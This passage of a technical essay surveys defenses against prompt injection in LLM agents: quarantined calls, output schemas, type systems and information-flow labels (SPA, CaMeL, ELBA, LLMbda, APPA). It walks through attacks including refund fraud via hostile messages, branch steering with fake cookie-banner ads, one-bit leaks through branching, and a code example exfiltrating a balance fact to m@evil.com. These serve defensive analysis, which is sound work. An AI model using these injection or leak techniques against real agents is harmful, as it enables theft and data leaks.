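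The recursive model that searched 40,000 old messages is an agent on both tests, because its root chooses each step after seeing earlier results. If `llm_query` began returning full sentences instead of product names, the root could detect this in the printed results and reword its question. But if the owner's software began discontinuing whichever product the root named in its final answer, the root would receive no information about this and would give the same answer. Kenton and colleagues suggest using adaptation as a test of which outcomes a system is trying to influence. By that test, the root is trying to produce a correct answer but not to change what the shop sells.

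The third program resembles Baya, the web agent that repairs its code after an error. If the payment provider starts to require a reason for each refund, the tool returns an error, the planner adds the reason and the refunds continue. If the tool silently pays the wrong account, nothing triggers a repair. The owner could have the program confirm after each refund that the money arrived, and the system would then respond to that fault too. So adding checks, which most engineers would regard as a safety measure, also makes the system more goal-directed. (A later section looks at ways to restrict what the planner sees and changes during a repair.)

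For the last program, suppose the owner wants to know which supplier to drop. One set of calls reads complaints and identifies the part that failed in each. Another reads invoices and identifies the company that supplied each part. Ordinary code matches the two lists and counts the failures. None of the calls receives the overall goal, and their answers would be the same whatever happened to the suppliers.

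Drexler argues that combining services doesn't automatically produce one large agent, and that fixed functions can't adjust their behavior to suit each other's purposes. He accepts that someone could combine services into a complete agent, and that there is no bright line between agents and non-agents. The supplier program would become more like an agent if it used each answer to choose the next question and continued until it found a way to end a contract. The whole program might then adapt to obstacles, even though each call received only a fragment of the task and no individual prompt contained the goal.

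### Deep recursion without tools: HCH

In 2016 the AI safety researcher Paul Christiano described an idealized system that takes this kind of division to an extreme. He called it HCH, for "humans consulting HCH". A person answers a question with the help of a machine, which answers any smaller question exactly as that same person would if they had the machine too. The result is a tree of copies of one person, each consulting further copies. For a tree of limited depth, one can write:

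HCH₀(q) = H(q)

HCH_d(q) = H(q, with access to HCH_d₋₁)

Here H(q) is the person's answer to question q, and d is the number of levels below the top. If each copy asks ten questions and d = 6, the tree contains 1,111,111 copies. Christiano's ideal version has no limit on depth. Nobody could build it, but he proposed training a model to approximate it by imitating a person who can consult the model.

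In the basic version, the copies have no tools. Each one reads a question, works on it for a limited time and writes an answer. Someone could reasonably say that such a tree has no goal of its own, since each copy is only trying to help with its question and none runs long enough to carry out a project.

A tree of helpful answers can still search for the best way to achieve something. Suppose the shop owner asks which email would bring back the most former customers. The top copy asks other copies to draft emails and has further copies compare them in pairs. Each of these further copies honestly answers a question such as "Which of these two would get more replies?" The winning email might threaten customers with the loss of an account they had forgotten about, even though no copy set out to frighten them.

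The test of Kenton and colleagues gives a mixed result for the tree. They count humans as agents because people usually change their behavior when they learn that its consequences have changed. If the question included the fact that the shop would send the email to 40,000 people without reading it first, the top copy might well choose a gentler email. A copy that receives only two drafts can't take this into account unless somebody passes the information down.

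Christiano hoped that a tree whose members are all trying to help would itself be trying to help. Yudkowsky, in a 2018 critique of his approach, doubted that safe parts would necessarily make a safe whole. In a familiar thought experiment, thousands of clerks run a chess program by hand, each following a rule about a few symbols. Together they play to win, even if none of them has heard of chess. Similarly, a tree of people answering small enough questions could carry out a plan that none of them understood.

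One response is for each copy to explain the purpose of its questions, so that the copies below can object to a purpose they dislike. This would probably catch the threatening email. But longer questions leave more room for text that misleads the reader, and a misleading answer can spread upward through the tree. For this reason, Christiano considered limiting how much each copy reads. A tighter limit means a copy can know less about the purpose of its work, which makes its position more like that of the clerks.

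The dispute rests almost entirely on thought experiments. The recursive language models in the previous section are the closest working systems, but studies of them measured accuracy on questions with known answers, where manipulating people would have gained little. Researchers would learn more by giving such a system an open-ended request, like the one about the email, and comparing its final answer with the input to each call.

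## Quarantined calls: what they prevent and what they leave open

Strangers' messages can mislead any model that reads them, but many useful tasks require a model to read them. The *dual-LLM pattern* splits such tasks between two models. A privileged model plans the task and can use tools but never sees untrusted data, while a quarantined model reads that data and has no tools. Foerster, Blanchard and colleagues (2026) credit the pattern to the programmer Simon Willison, who described it in April 2023.

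The two models can be the same model called in two ways. Girrens and Wang used one small OpenAI model, GPT-5.4 nano, both to write SPA's plans and to read untrusted text. The software separates the two uses by controlling what each call receives and what happens to its answer.

The pattern works with or without a fixed plan. In CaMeL, as Girrens and Wang describe it, the privileged model turns the user's request into a complete program and never receives the values that the program produces. Fides calls its planner again for every step but hides the tools' results from it. Foerster and colleagues adapted both systems to operate a computer. The CaMeL version used 1.88 times as many tokens as an agent with no defense, and the Fides version used 29.6 times as many because it sent the planner the full history at every step.

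### The rules of quarantine

A quarantined call is a language-model function with extra restrictions on its answer. Piet and colleagues set these rules for the model calls in their web programs:

- The call has no tools.
- The program declares an output schema in advance, and the interpreter rejects any answer that doesn't fit it.
- The program stores the answer in a variable.
- The interpreter never executes the answer.

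The call also can't change the program or the set of tools the program may use.

SPA has a dedicated type of step for quarantined calls. It writes plans in JSON, a standard format for structured data, and the call in the refund program would look roughly like this:

```
{"type": "q-llm",
 "inputs": ["message.text"],
 "prompt": "Is a broken item reported?",
 "schema": {"type": "boolean"},
 "output": "broken",
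 "intent": "Decide whether to refund the customer",
 "output_semantics": "True if the message reports a broken item"}
```

The model receives only this step's inputs and prompt, so it has no record of earlier messages. SPA keeps the answer after the run, but a later planner sees only the answer's schema and the descriptions in the last two fields, which the first planner wrote before any model read the message. If the owner asks the next day for a list of customers with broken items, the new planner can identify which stored values it needs without seeing them.

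SPA stops the whole run when a value doesn't fit its schema, so if message 17 caused the model to return a paragraph instead of true or false, the 33 customers after it would get no refund. Software can prevent this by restricting the model to valid answers as it writes.

A schema can also be so loose that it restricts almost nothing. If a schema allows any string, an attacker's entire email is a valid answer. Piet and colleagues point out that declaring a field a string doesn't show whether it contains a price, an account number or text written by a stranger.

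Quarantine protects the planner only if untrusted text can't reach it by another route, such as the descriptions of its tools. Piet and colleagues describe this risk when a developer has a language model write tools for a website. If the model reads live pages while writing the tools, a hostile review could influence the code. A `get_reviews` tool might then also send data to the attacker, and every later program that used it would have the same flaw. The researchers propose that people write such tools by hand or check them before a planner can use them.

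SPA has an optional mode that hides the installed tools from the planner. The planner invents the tools its plan needs, and software then looks for installed ones that match. About 75% of these runs failed because the software found no match, and the share of tasks completed fell from 53.0% to 14.1%.

### One hostile message, three ways

Suppose an attacker whose $50 order arrived intact wrote message 17 in the shop owner's inbox, and the model that reads it does whatever the attacker wants. The attacker's gain depends on which version of the refund program the owner is running.

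In the sub-agent version, the attacker can collect any refunds the tool permits until the sub-agent reaches its turn limit. The sub-agent can also look up other customers' orders. It has no tool for sending messages, but it can pass information through the amount of a refund, since a payment of $4,821.07 gives its recipient six digits. The attack ends when the sub-agent returns, because message 18 goes to a new sub-agent with no memory of message 17.

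In the version that calls the planner again, the attacker might get the whole customer list. The new steps may also change variables that the rest of the program uses. If they overwrite the owner's request, the planner will also read a false request when it handles messages 18 to 50.

*On the Relative Security of Prompt Injection* includes a case in which this kind of interference is enough by itself to leak a secret. An injected program calls no tools and only copies the secret into the variable that holds the text of a reply. The original plan then sends the reply as planned. Running injected steps on a copy of the variables and then discarding the copy prevents this.

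With a quarantined yes/no call, the attacker gains $50 and can't affect the answer for any other message.

An attacker can get up to $50 per message. The program never checks whether it has already refunded an order, so someone who sent 50 messages about the same $50 order could collect $2,500, unless the refund tool rejects repeat refunds. Quarantine doesn't prevent this because all 50 calls would have followed the rules. A line of ordinary code that tracks which orders the program has refunded would fix it.

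### Quarantined calls that choose the next step

An earlier section gave four conditions that together rebuild the agent loop: feedback, selection, repetition and range. A quarantined model can still select actions, because the program can carry out the action that the model names, even though the model itself has no tools.

The switch program from that section follows every quarantine rule, but its model still chooses a tool and its arguments on each of the 20 turns.

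A much stricter schema doesn't change this. Suppose the planner writes eight complete steps, including all their arguments, and the call can only pick one of them:

```
for turn in range(20):
    step = quarantined("Which step comes next?", request, history)
    result = steps[step]()
    history.append((step, result))
```

If the program made this choice only once, there would be eight possible outcomes. Over 20 turns there are 8²⁰ sequences, or about 10¹⁸. The history includes the results of earlier steps, so an attacker's message in one result can influence every later choice. The attacker can't add a ninth step, but may be able to combine the eight in an unforeseen order, such as reading the customer list and then posting the latest result to a public page.

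The refund program avoids this because it maps each answer to a narrow choice, whether to make one particular payment. Its calls also receive no history. Quarantine removes selection only when the surrounding program is this restrictive, so a reviewer has to read the code that uses the answer as well as the call. (The next section covers systems that let sub-agents keep their tools and use labels to restrict them.)

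### Wrong values

A schema checks the form of an answer but not whether it is true. Piet and colleagues give the example of an agent that approves changes to a software project after asking a quarantined model whether the code is valid. A hostile change could trick the model into returning "yes", which fits the schema.

They treat some false answers as outside the scope of their defense. If a seller floods a product page with fake praise, they consider that a problem with the information on the page, because it might mislead a human shopper too. If a review gets the agent to ignore the user's $200 limit and buy $2,000 headphones, they consider that within scope, because the review exploits the model. Both kinds of false answer can cause the same loss, since a shop loses $50 whether a customer lies about a broken mug or manipulates the model.

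Ordinary code can limit how wrong a value can be. If the refund program asked the model for the price of the broken item, an attacker could choose any number the schema allowed. A schema that accepted only numbers from 0 to 50 would keep the old limit. The program as written is safer still because it takes the price from the shop's records instead of from the model.

SPA handles wrong values by tracking where each value came from. A label on each value records how trustworthy its sources are, and the answer from a quarantined call is only as trustworthy as its least trusted input. A summary of a stranger's email is therefore as untrusted as the email. Otherwise, a program could turn untrusted text into trusted text by having a model rewrite it.

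SPA also labels everything inside a branch as untrusted if the branch depends on an untrusted answer, and it does the same for a loop over untrusted items. If the refund tool accepted only trusted inputs, SPA would therefore reject the refund program before the first message, and neither the attacker nor honest customers would get refunds.

On AgentDojo, turning on the label checks reduced the share of tasks completed when there was no attack from 53.0% to 29.0%. SPA rejected about 53% of all its runs for breaking the label rules, usually because a plan passed untrusted tool output to a tool that required trusted input. Successful attacks fell from four out of 949 (0.4%) to zero.

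These figures are weak evidence that the checks aren't worth using, because the attacker in this test mostly tries to get the agent to make extra tool calls, which SPA's fixed plan already prevents. A better test of the labels would use an attacker who supplies false account numbers or false answers.

### Branch steering

A false answer can also send a program down the wrong branch. Foerster and colleagues call it *branch steering* when an attacker manipulates what a model perceives so that the plan takes a harmful branch it already contains. They studied it in agents that operate a computer by looking at the screen and clicking.

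In their system, the planner writes a whole program before it sees the screen. While the program runs, a quarantined model that can read images describes what is on the screen. Another quarantined call compares the description with something the planner expected and returns true or false. A small part of such a plan might look like this:

```
screen = describe_screen()
if verify("A cookie banner is visible", screen):
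    x, y = find("the button that closes the cookie banner")
    click(x, y)
```

This approach requires the planner to anticipate many situations in advance. The plans averaged 213 lines of code, 41 tool calls and 40 branches, compared with 52 lines, five tool calls and four branches for CaMeL's plans on AgentDojo. Roughly half of each plan consisted of fallbacks that a given run never used. The fallbacks make the agent more reliable, but each one also gives an attacker another branch to try to trigger.

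Foerster and colleagues demonstrated two attacks that used advertisements on web pages. The first advertisement looked like a cookie banner, and the agent clicked it and went to the attacker's site. This attack required little knowledge of the user's task because nearly every browsing plan deals with cookie banners early. In the second attack, they altered an advertisement's pixels so that the image-reading model returned false coordinates with a plausible explanation.

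They also tried two defenses. One compared the model's answer with the web page's code, which often labels advertisements as such. It caught the fake cookie banner in one common advertising format but missed it in another, where the attacker could replace the label. The other used independent models to check the answer. These models had trouble telling fake cookie banners from real ones without also blocking legitimate clicks, and they missed the altered pixels even on a setting that produced many false alarms. This defense also raised token use from 1.88 times that of an undefended agent to 6.57 times.

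These tests assumed a strong attacker who knows the task and the tools and can roughly predict the plan. Foerster and colleagues also left out the security policies that CaMeL and Fides normally apply, because it is hard to write a useful policy for a click. Attacks are harder when they require several false answers in a row or depend on the details of one plan, so a fake cookie banner alone probably wouldn't be enough to redirect a bank transfer.

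The fake banner did its damage mostly through wrong coordinates. The plan rightly included a click from the start to close any cookie banner, but the click's effect depended on coordinates from a model that was looking at the attacker's advertisement. As Piet and colleagues say of this work, fixing the program in advance doesn't fix what an action on the screen means. They would give programs named operations such as `refund`, whose effects are known in advance. An attacker can still steer such a program, but only among effects that a reviewer could have found in the plan.

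The isolation also made the agents less capable. Claude Sonnet 4.5, a 2025 model, solved 109 of the benchmark's automatically scored tasks without any defense. The isolated version solved 31 of those tasks on its first attempt and 62 in at least one of five attempts. Foerster and colleagues report the 62 tasks as retaining 57% of the undefended performance, which assumes that something can pick out the successful attempt.

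### Leaks through branching

A quarantined call can help leak private data if it reads the data together with untrusted text. *On the Relative Security of Prompt Injection* examines such leaks by comparing an agent with the reference agent described earlier, which never obeys untrusted text. The agent counts as secure if an attacker can't use it to tell apart two secrets that they couldn't tell apart using the reference agent. A proof assistant, software that checks mathematical proofs, verified each result.

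In the simplest example, the plan reads the user's private notes and an email from a stranger, asks a quarantined model for a reply based on both, and sends the reply to the stranger. Without an attack, the reply would depend only on the email. If the email misleads the model, the model can quote the notes in its reply. The model doesn't need a tool to leak them, because the plan already sends its reply.

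Labels can stop this leak. In the next version, the interpreter marks the notes as private, marks any answer computed from them as private too, and blocks private values from being sent to strangers. This prevents the leak whatever the quarantined model does, unless the attacker can see the contents of blocked messages, for instance in an error log. However, the plan can no longer reply to email, because a legitimate reply also has the notes among its inputs.

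The third version, called Tagged Branch, gets around the labels:

```
answer = quarantined(question, notes, email)
if answer == 1:
    send(stranger, 1)
else:
    send(stranger, 0)
```

The numbers 1 and 0 in the last lines are part of the plan's text, so they are public and the interpreter lets the program send either one. But a misled model can return 1 exactly when the notes have some property the attacker cares about. The stranger then learns one bit about the notes from which number arrives. Deleting one of the two `send` lines wouldn't prevent this, because the stranger could learn the same thing from whether a message arrived.

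Closing this channel requires the labels to follow control flow as well as data. CaMeL has a strict mode designed to do this, though the proofs cover only its normal mode. SPA's treatment of branches has the same effect for confidentiality. It would mark both `send` steps as depending on the notes and reject the plan if the `send` tool may receive only public data.

The easiest fix for this plan is to leave the notes out of the call, since the correct answer depends only on the email. The refund program already does this, because each call reads only one message and the customer who wrote it knows what it contains. If the owner added her staff's private remarks about each customer so that the model could spot people who complain too often, each refund could reveal one bit of those remarks.

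### How much an answer can carry

A call whose schema allows N possible answers can leak at most log₂ N bits. The table shows how many calls an attacker would need to learn a six-digit code, assuming that the calls can read the code and the attacker can tell which answer each one gave.

| Form of the answer | Possible answers | Bits per call | Calls to reveal a six-digit code |
|---|---|---|---|
| Yes or no | 2 | 1 | 20 |
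| One of eight options | 8 | 3 | 7 |
| Any date from year 1 to year 9999 | About 3.65 million | 21.8 | 1 |
| 500 characters of free text | About 10⁹⁸⁹ | About 3,285 | 1 |

Even a date can carry a six-digit code if the schema doesn't limit the year. Allowing only the next 30 days would reduce its capacity to less than five bits. A yes/no answer is the narrowest useful schema, but 50 such answers in one run can still carry up to 50 bits.

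These figures are upper limits. The attacker learns less if several answers lead to the same visible action, and nothing if they can't observe the result. Timing can add to what they learn, since one branch may take noticeably longer than another.

Counting bits can also reveal leaks that a comparison with the reference agent misses. *On the Relative Security of Prompt Injection* gives the example of a plan that lets a stranger guess a secret and replies only whether the guess was right. Suppose an injection makes the agent send the entire secret. This still counts as secure, because for any two secrets there is a guess that would have told them apart. But a stranger who had to find a six-digit code by honest guessing would need about 500,000 attempts on average, and the injection provides it in one message. (The paper also defines a stricter version of security that rejects this example.)

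The same numbers limit how much influence can flow in the other direction. A stranger who controls a yes/no answer can choose between two branches that the planner wrote. With 500 characters of free text, they can write an email that goes out under the owner's name, or instructions for a later model call that has tools. Free text is risky even when only the owner reads it, because an attacker could use a summary to tell her to phone their number. SPA therefore applies its label rules to anything it displays and blanks out the parts that break them.

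### How bounded the damage is

Piet and colleagues argue that quarantine limits the damage. In their example, an agent searches a forum for posts that recommend a single book. A user who recommends several books could phrase a post so that the model counts it as recommending only one. The agent's list would then wrongly include that post, but the attacker couldn't get the agent to do anything outside its program.

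The refund program can lose at most $2,500, by issuing 50 refunds of $50 each. If only some of the messages are hostile and the model handles the rest correctly, the loss is at most $50 per hostile message, or $150 for three. These limits apply to a single run, so if the program ran every morning and nobody noticed the fraud, it could lose up to $912,500 in a year.

Limiting the size of a call's answer limits how precisely an attacker can steer the program, but the possible damage depends on the most harmful action the answer can trigger. If the plan deletes the customer database when the answer is "yes", an attacker needs to control only one bit to destroy it. However, a call that returns 3,285 bits of free text may do no harm if the program only counts the words in it.

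Some actions also have effects that continue after the program ends. In the example of the agent that approves code, the program may only be able to approve or reject a change. If it approves a hostile one, that code may later run on thousands of other machines and do things that the program had no tools for. Piet and colleagues are right that the attacker can't add an action to the program, but in this case the attacker needs only the approval action that is already there.

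The owner could cut the worst case to a fifth by having the program stop after $500 of refunds. But ten hostile messages at the top of the inbox could use up that money before any honest customer got a refund. *On the Relative Security of Prompt Injection* includes a similar case, in which an agent may send only one message per run. If the model is misled into sending a different message first, the monitor that enforces the limit blocks the reply the user wanted.

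The owner could instead have the program collect all the "yes" answers and show her the list before it pays anyone. She would see up to 50 names and amounts, and she would probably notice if the same customer appeared 50 times. This would help much less with the agent that approves code, because a list of approved changes would look normal even if one was hostile, and somebody would have to read the code to find it.

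## Allowing recursion under types and information-flow labels

Quarantine takes away a model's tools, but some jobs need them, such as checking a customer's earlier orders before paying a refund. Several research groups have tried to keep sub-agents with tools, and even planners that write new steps mid-run, by restricting what nested calls can do instead of forbidding them. Some restrictions are *types*, which limit the actions a piece of code can contain. Software checks them before the code runs. Other restrictions are *information-flow labels*, which record where a value came from and who may see it. Software usually checks these during the run.

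### Types that limit actions

ELBA, the Haskell system in which a model's program can call the model again, runs a generated program only if it passes a type check. In Haskell, types describe both the form of a value, such as a number or a date, and a program's *effects*. Effects are the program's interactions with the outside world, such as reading a file or sending money.

Zhou and colleagues give the example of a calculator on a public website that passes each question to a model and requires an integer in return. A visitor asks it to delete every file on the server and then compute the factorial of 5, and the model writes a program that does both. The program never runs because it has the wrong type. Any Haskell code that deletes a file has the type `IO`, for input and output, and so does any larger program that contains it, but the calculator requires a plain `Int`. ELBA returns the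 type error to the model, which tries again.

A calculator needs no effects, but most agents do. For these, a developer defines a new effect type that covers only a few chosen operations. The shop owner's developer might write this library:

```
findOrder    :: Customer -> Shop [Order]
trackParcel  :: Order -> Shop Status
refundSender :: Message -> Shop ()
```

`Shop` is the new effect type, and `()` means that a function returns no value. `refundSender` makes a single payment of up to $50 to the customer who wrote the message. The sub-agent in the refund program becomes a call that must produce a program of type `Shop ()`. The model can write any loops and calculations and use the three operations in any order. A program that also emails the customer list fails the type check, because no email function has the type `Shop`.

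Types can also control which values reach an operation. ELBA's bibliography assistant may save only entries from the DBLP database, so its library gives each fetched entry the type `Trusted Bib`. Only the library can create values of that type, which prevents the model from inventing an entry and saving it. In a test with 100 computer science topics, Zhou and colleagues found no wrong author, year or identifier among the assistant's 925 citations. An ordinary agent with a web search tool made such a mistake in 19 of 1,002 citations. The type guarantees that an entry came from DBLP, but not that it is relevant to the topic.

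### What a nested call inherits

The last line of the bibliography program from an earlier section calls the model again. Haskell infers from the surrounding code that this call has type `BibIO ()`, where `BibIO` is the bibliography library's effect type. The program that the model writes in response must therefore pass the same check as the first, and so must every program that it requests in turn.

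A parent can set a tighter limit for its child than it has itself, but not a looser one. The shop's sub-agent could ask another model call for a `Bool`, true or false, and that call could do nothing except answer. The sub-agent couldn't ask for a program of type `IO ()`, which could do anything, because the request would itself have the type `IO ()` and Haskell would reject it inside a `Shop` program.

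Effect types also solve a problem with DSPy, where changing one line turned a language-model function into a sub-agent without changing its signature. In ELBA, a call that may use tools has a different type from one that may not, so a reviewer can tell them apart by type.

### The guarantee and its proof

Zhou and colleagues prove that adding agent calls to a language preserves the guarantees of its type system. They define the *trace* of a run as the sequence of tool calls with visible effects outside the program. If the type system ensures something about the traces of every ordinary program of type t, for example that no trace includes sending an email, then the same is true of every program of type t that contains agent calls, as long as each generated program passes the type check before it runs.

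The proof replaces agent calls with ordinary code. Every call has a depth n, which limits how far the recursion below it can go. Let aₙ be the ordinary code that replaces a call of depth n:

- a₀ returns nothing.
- aₙ₊₁ asks the model for a program and returns nothing if the program fails the type check. If the program passes, aₙ₊₁ replaces every agent call in it with the matching aₘ, where m ≤ n, and runs the result.

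A call of depth 0 does nothing, so a₀ has the same trace. Assume that replacements up to depth n have the same traces as the calls they replace. A program generated at depth n + 1 contains only calls of depth n or less, so replacing them does not change the program's externally observable behavior. By induction, replacement preserves traces at every depth. The result is an ordinary program of type t, which the type system's existing guarantee covers.

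This proof treats the model as an arbitrary function from prompts to programs, so the result holds even if an attacker writes every program. However, the result depends on other software being correct. Generated code must stay within a subset of Haskell that excludes functions such as `unsafePerformIO`, which hide effects from the type checker. The library functions must also do what the developer intended. If the developer forgot the $50 limit in `refundSender`, the model could pay refunds of any size without violating the theorem.

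### Sub-agents that keep their tools

A type check runs before the program has read anything, so it can't account for what the program reads later. ELBA tracks this at run time with LIO, an existing Haskell library for information flow. LIO keeps a *current label* for the running code, which combines the labels of everything the code has read. If a program reads a page from phony.com, its current label records that this site has influenced it. If the program then tries to write to a destination that accepts only data the user trusts, LIO stops it partway through with an error, even though it passed the type check.

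With this rule alone, one untrusted message could restrict everything the program did afterwards. LIO's `toLabeled` function avoids that by running part of the program separately, with its own current label. The result comes back sealed, with its label attached, and the outer program can pass it on without opening it or changing its own label.

The dual-LLM pattern is the special case in which the separate part is a model with no tools. With labels, a sub-agent can keep its tools, because each tool checks the current label before it acts. In Zhou and colleagues' example, a sub-agent drafts a direct message and may read untrusted text and call tools while it works. The outer agent passes the sealed draft, without reading it, to a `sendDM` tool, which checks the recipient and the text's label before sending it.

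A sub-agent may lose access to most of its tools after reading a stranger's message. ELBA's policy for workplace chat lowers a model's privileges to those of whoever wrote the data it has just read. If applied strictly to the shop, this policy would block every refund, because customers can't authorize their own refunds.

### A worst-case test

Zhou and colleagues tested the policies on the altered version of ELBA mentioned earlier, in which a sub-agent that encounters an injection receives the injected data as its entire prompt. They ran each of the 105 combinations of user task and injection in AgentDojo's Slack suite seven times, for 735 runs per model.

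| Model | Injections resisted, without policies | Injections resisted, with policies | Tasks completed, without policies | Tasks completed, with policies |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Opus 4.7 | 425 | 735 | 523 | 351 |
| Opus 4.8 | 460 | 735 | 557 | 312 |
| GPT 5.4 | 621 | 735 | 558 | 338 |
| Sonnet 5 | 540 | 735 | 494 | 294 |

The alteration skips the hard part of an attack, which is persuading the model. Without it, current models resisted all of AgentDojo's attacks, so the test would have revealed little about the policies. But the injected instructions came from AgentDojo and were written without knowledge of ELBA's policies. An attacker who knew the policies would look for a harmful action that they permit.

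The perfect scores also reflect a correction. AgentDojo's scoring program counted 29 of the 2,940 runs with policies as successful attacks because the agent had opened a web address that the attacker supplied. Zhou and colleagues reviewed all 29 and found no violation. Their policies would have blocked the request if the address had contained private data or if the agent had already read something sensitive.

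Across the four models, ELBA completed 73% of tasks without policies and 44% with them. The figures were almost the same when nobody attacked, at 64 of 84 runs (76%) without policies and 37 of 84 (44%) with them, so the attacks explain little of the difference. Labels block actions based on where the data came from, so they stop a colleague's honest request as well as an attacker's. CaMeL dropped even further, from 61 of 84 runs to 20, when its own policies were on.

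Zhou and colleagues suggest letting actions that pass the policies go ahead and having a person review the rest. If approval allowed every task that the policies blocked here to succeed, a person would have to step in on about a third of ordinary tasks. That is far better than approving every action, but the assistant would still be far from working alone.

### Labels on the conversation

The LLMbda calculus, the small language whose retry loop appeared in an earlier section, puts labels on the conversation with the model as well as on data. Garby, Gordon and Sands (2026), in *AI Agents, Conversations, and Information Flow*, a revised account of the language, add a few operations to a minimal functional language:

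- `@` sends a prompt, receives the reply and evaluates it as data or code.
- `fork` runs an expression on a copy of the conversation and then discards the copy.
- `clear` empties the conversation.
- A label expression marks a value as, for instance, untrusted or secret.
- `assert` stops the program unless a value's label permits the intended use.

A programmer can build a quarantined call by forking the conversation, clearing the copy and prompting the model there, but the language doesn't require this. A program can instead add a stranger's email to the main conversation, but then every later reply in that conversation is labeled "untrusted", and so are the results of any code in those replies.

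Garby and colleagues wanted proofs because label tracking is easy to get wrong. They found a leak in CaMeL that follows a pattern known since the 1970s. Suppose a stranger wants to know whether an account balance is above some threshold. The leak works roughly like this:

```
rich = True
tmp = True
if account.balance > threshold: tmp = False
if tmp: rich = False
if rich: send_email("m@evil.com", "rich!")
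```

CaMeL marks a variable as private when a branch that depends on private data changes it. If the balance is high, the first branch runs, so `tmp` becomes false and private. The second branch then doesn't run, so `rich` stays true and public. CaMeL therefore treats the last condition as public and sends the email. If the balance is low, `rich` becomes false and no email goes out. The stranger can therefore tell whether the balance is high by whether the email arrives.

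In LLMbda, the conversation is the only thing a program can change in this way. The interpreter stops any program that tries to change a public conversation from inside a branch that depends on a secret.

#### What the theorem covers

The main theorem is a form of *noninterference*. If you run a program twice with inputs that differ only in their secrets, the public results have the same probabilities in both runs, except for differences in how often the program fails to finish. The theorem also covers trust. Replacing a stranger's message with a different one doesn't change the probabilities of results labelled as trusted, with the same exception. The theorem applies to every program in the language, including programs that generate code and run it.

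The proof compares the real interpreter with an imaginary one that skips any step that involves data hidden from the observer and substitutes an empty value. The imaginary interpreter never uses the hidden data, so it behaves identically on two inputs that differ only in that data. It also produces each visible result at least as often as the real one, because it never gets stuck on a hidden step. Its probabilities are therefore upper limits for the real interpreter on both inputs, and the real interpreter's results can differ between the inputs only through runs that produce no result. A proof assistant checked the argument, and the interpreter in the proof is the one that runs the agents.

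This exception makes the theorem *termination-insensitive*. If the program fails to finish with probability p on one secret and q on the other, the distance between the two distributions of visible results is at most (p + q)/2 by a standard measure. If the program always finishes, the distributions are identical. A run that stops for a policy violation counts as unfinished, so an attacker who can see that a run stopped may learn one bit about a secret.

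Leaking one bit is usually tolerable, but a program that retries can leak another bit with each attempt. CaMeL's retry loop is ordinary Python outside the part that tracks labels, and Garby and colleagues point out that an attacker could use it to extract a whole secret one bit at a time. LLMbda programs can retry inside the language, where labels carry over from one attempt to the next.

### Endorsement

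Strict labels would stop the refund program, because its decision to pay depends on text from strangers. LLMbda's `endorse` operation lets the program make an exception by declaring an untrusted value trusted enough to use. In Python-like notation, the program might contain:

```
answer = quarantine("Is a broken item reported?", message.text)
if endorse(answer == "yes"):
    refund(message.customer, min(message.order_price, 50))
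```

The worst case is again 50 refunds of $50. Unlike the earlier program, this one lets reviewers find each place where a stranger's text influences a protected action by searching the code for `endorse`. Fides, by contrast, has an optional setting that lets through any answer with only a few possible values. Garby and colleagues object that nobody can then tell an intended exception from a leak.

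Endorsing a value makes it trusted but doesn't make it public. If the answer above also depended on the staff's private remarks, it would still be labeled "secret" after endorsement. Garby and colleagues prove that secrets stay protected regardless of how many endorsements occur or what the untrusted input contains. There is no such guarantee for trust, because the purpose of endorsement is to let untrusted data be treated as trusted.

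They tested endorsement with an agent called Randori on AgentDojo's banking tasks. Randori's planner writes the endorsements into its program before it reads any untrusted data. With the model Qwen3.7-plus, the agent completed 36 of 48 runs with endorsement and 30 without. With MiMo-v2.5, it completed 31 with endorsement and 26 without. The runs cover only 16 different tasks, so the size of the gain is uncertain. The gain clearly comes from three tasks that require the agent to read a file and act on its contents, which strict labels forbid.

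Only two of 1,296 attacks on Randori succeeded. This result overstates the labels' effect, because 873 of the attacks needed an action that would never appear in a plan for the user's task, so planning in advance would generally have stopped them anyway. That left 423 for the labels and the model's own resistance to stop. In both successful attacks, the user had asked the agent to read a file and make the payment described there, and the attacker had replaced the file's contents with a different payment request. The planner had endorsed whatever the file contained. Without endorsement, the labels blocked this attack, but they would also have blocked the legitimate payment.

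### Child branches with bounded answers

LLMbda and ELBA require a model to write in an unusual language. *APPA* (Kravchenko, Liventsev and colleagues, 2026) instead adds labels to an ordinary agent loop. Software between the agent and its tools checks each call before it goes out and each result before the model reads it.

A label in APPA is a pair (R, t), where R is the set of people who may see the data and t is its level of trust. Data from two sources gets the label

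(R, t) ∧ (R′, t′) = (R ∩ R′, min(t, t′))

Suppose the personnel department and the finance director may read one file, and the accounts department and the finance director may read another. Only the finance director may receive a summary of both. When an agent reads more data, this can never widen the set of permitted readers or raise the level of trust. An agent that reads a single post on a public forum may therefore lose access to internal tools for the rest of its task.

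The agent can avoid this by doing the reading in a *child branch*, a temporary copy of itself. In one test task, the agent has to read a public thread about software timeouts and then file an internal ticket. A child can read the thread and report back without changing the parent's label.

The child starts with the parent's conversation and label. If the child started with a clean label instead, an agent could read the payroll, create a child whose conversation included the figures, and have the child email them to anybody.

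When the child finishes, the parent can discard or accept its result. Accepting an ordinary result v changes the parent's label from L to L ∧ label(v), so the parent takes on v's restrictions too. To keep its label unchanged, the parent can fix a strict schema before the child reads anything. The schema may allow yes/no answers, numbers within a range and choices from a closed list, but not free text. Kravchenko and colleagues stress that a misled child can still return a false answer that fits the schema. The people who deploy the system decide in advance whether to treat answers that fit the schema as trusted, and doing so in effect endorses them.

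Discarding a child doesn't undo its actions. If a child refunds an order and the parent then discards the child, the customer keeps the money. APPA records completed actions in a log that all branches share, so a rule against refunding the same order twice would still apply to the parent and to later children. The refund program lacked this check. A refund can be missing from the log if the payment goes through but the tool never reports a clear outcome.

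Kravchenko and colleagues tested three models on 20 office tasks that the researchers had designed themselves. The models completed 535 of 600 runs, and no attacks succeeded. Control versions with permissive policies completed 90% to 92.5% of runs, but attacks succeeded in 30% to 39.5%. When the researchers removed child branches, the completion rate for GPT-5.6 Luna fell from 88% to 56.5%.

APPA's policies seem to reduce task completion much less than ELBA's, but the comparison isn't fair because Kravchenko and colleagues wrote both the tasks and the policies, and designed the tasks to exercise APPA's features. On AgentThreatBench, an existing set of security tests, APPA completed between 64.2% and 76.7% of runs, again with no successful attacks.

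### Calling the planner again after an error

ELBA and APPA let a model read untrusted data and then restrict what it can do. Baya, the web agent that repairs its own programs, restricts what the planner reads. When a program fails on the live site, the planner can write a replacement, up to three times per task, using only the old program and a restricted error report. In an example from Chow and colleagues, a product search fails and the error report identifies the cause as a category filter that the site doesn't support, so the planner can write a search without it. The old program is safe for the planner to read because the planner wrote it before anything ran. A program may also report how many results it found, but not what they were.

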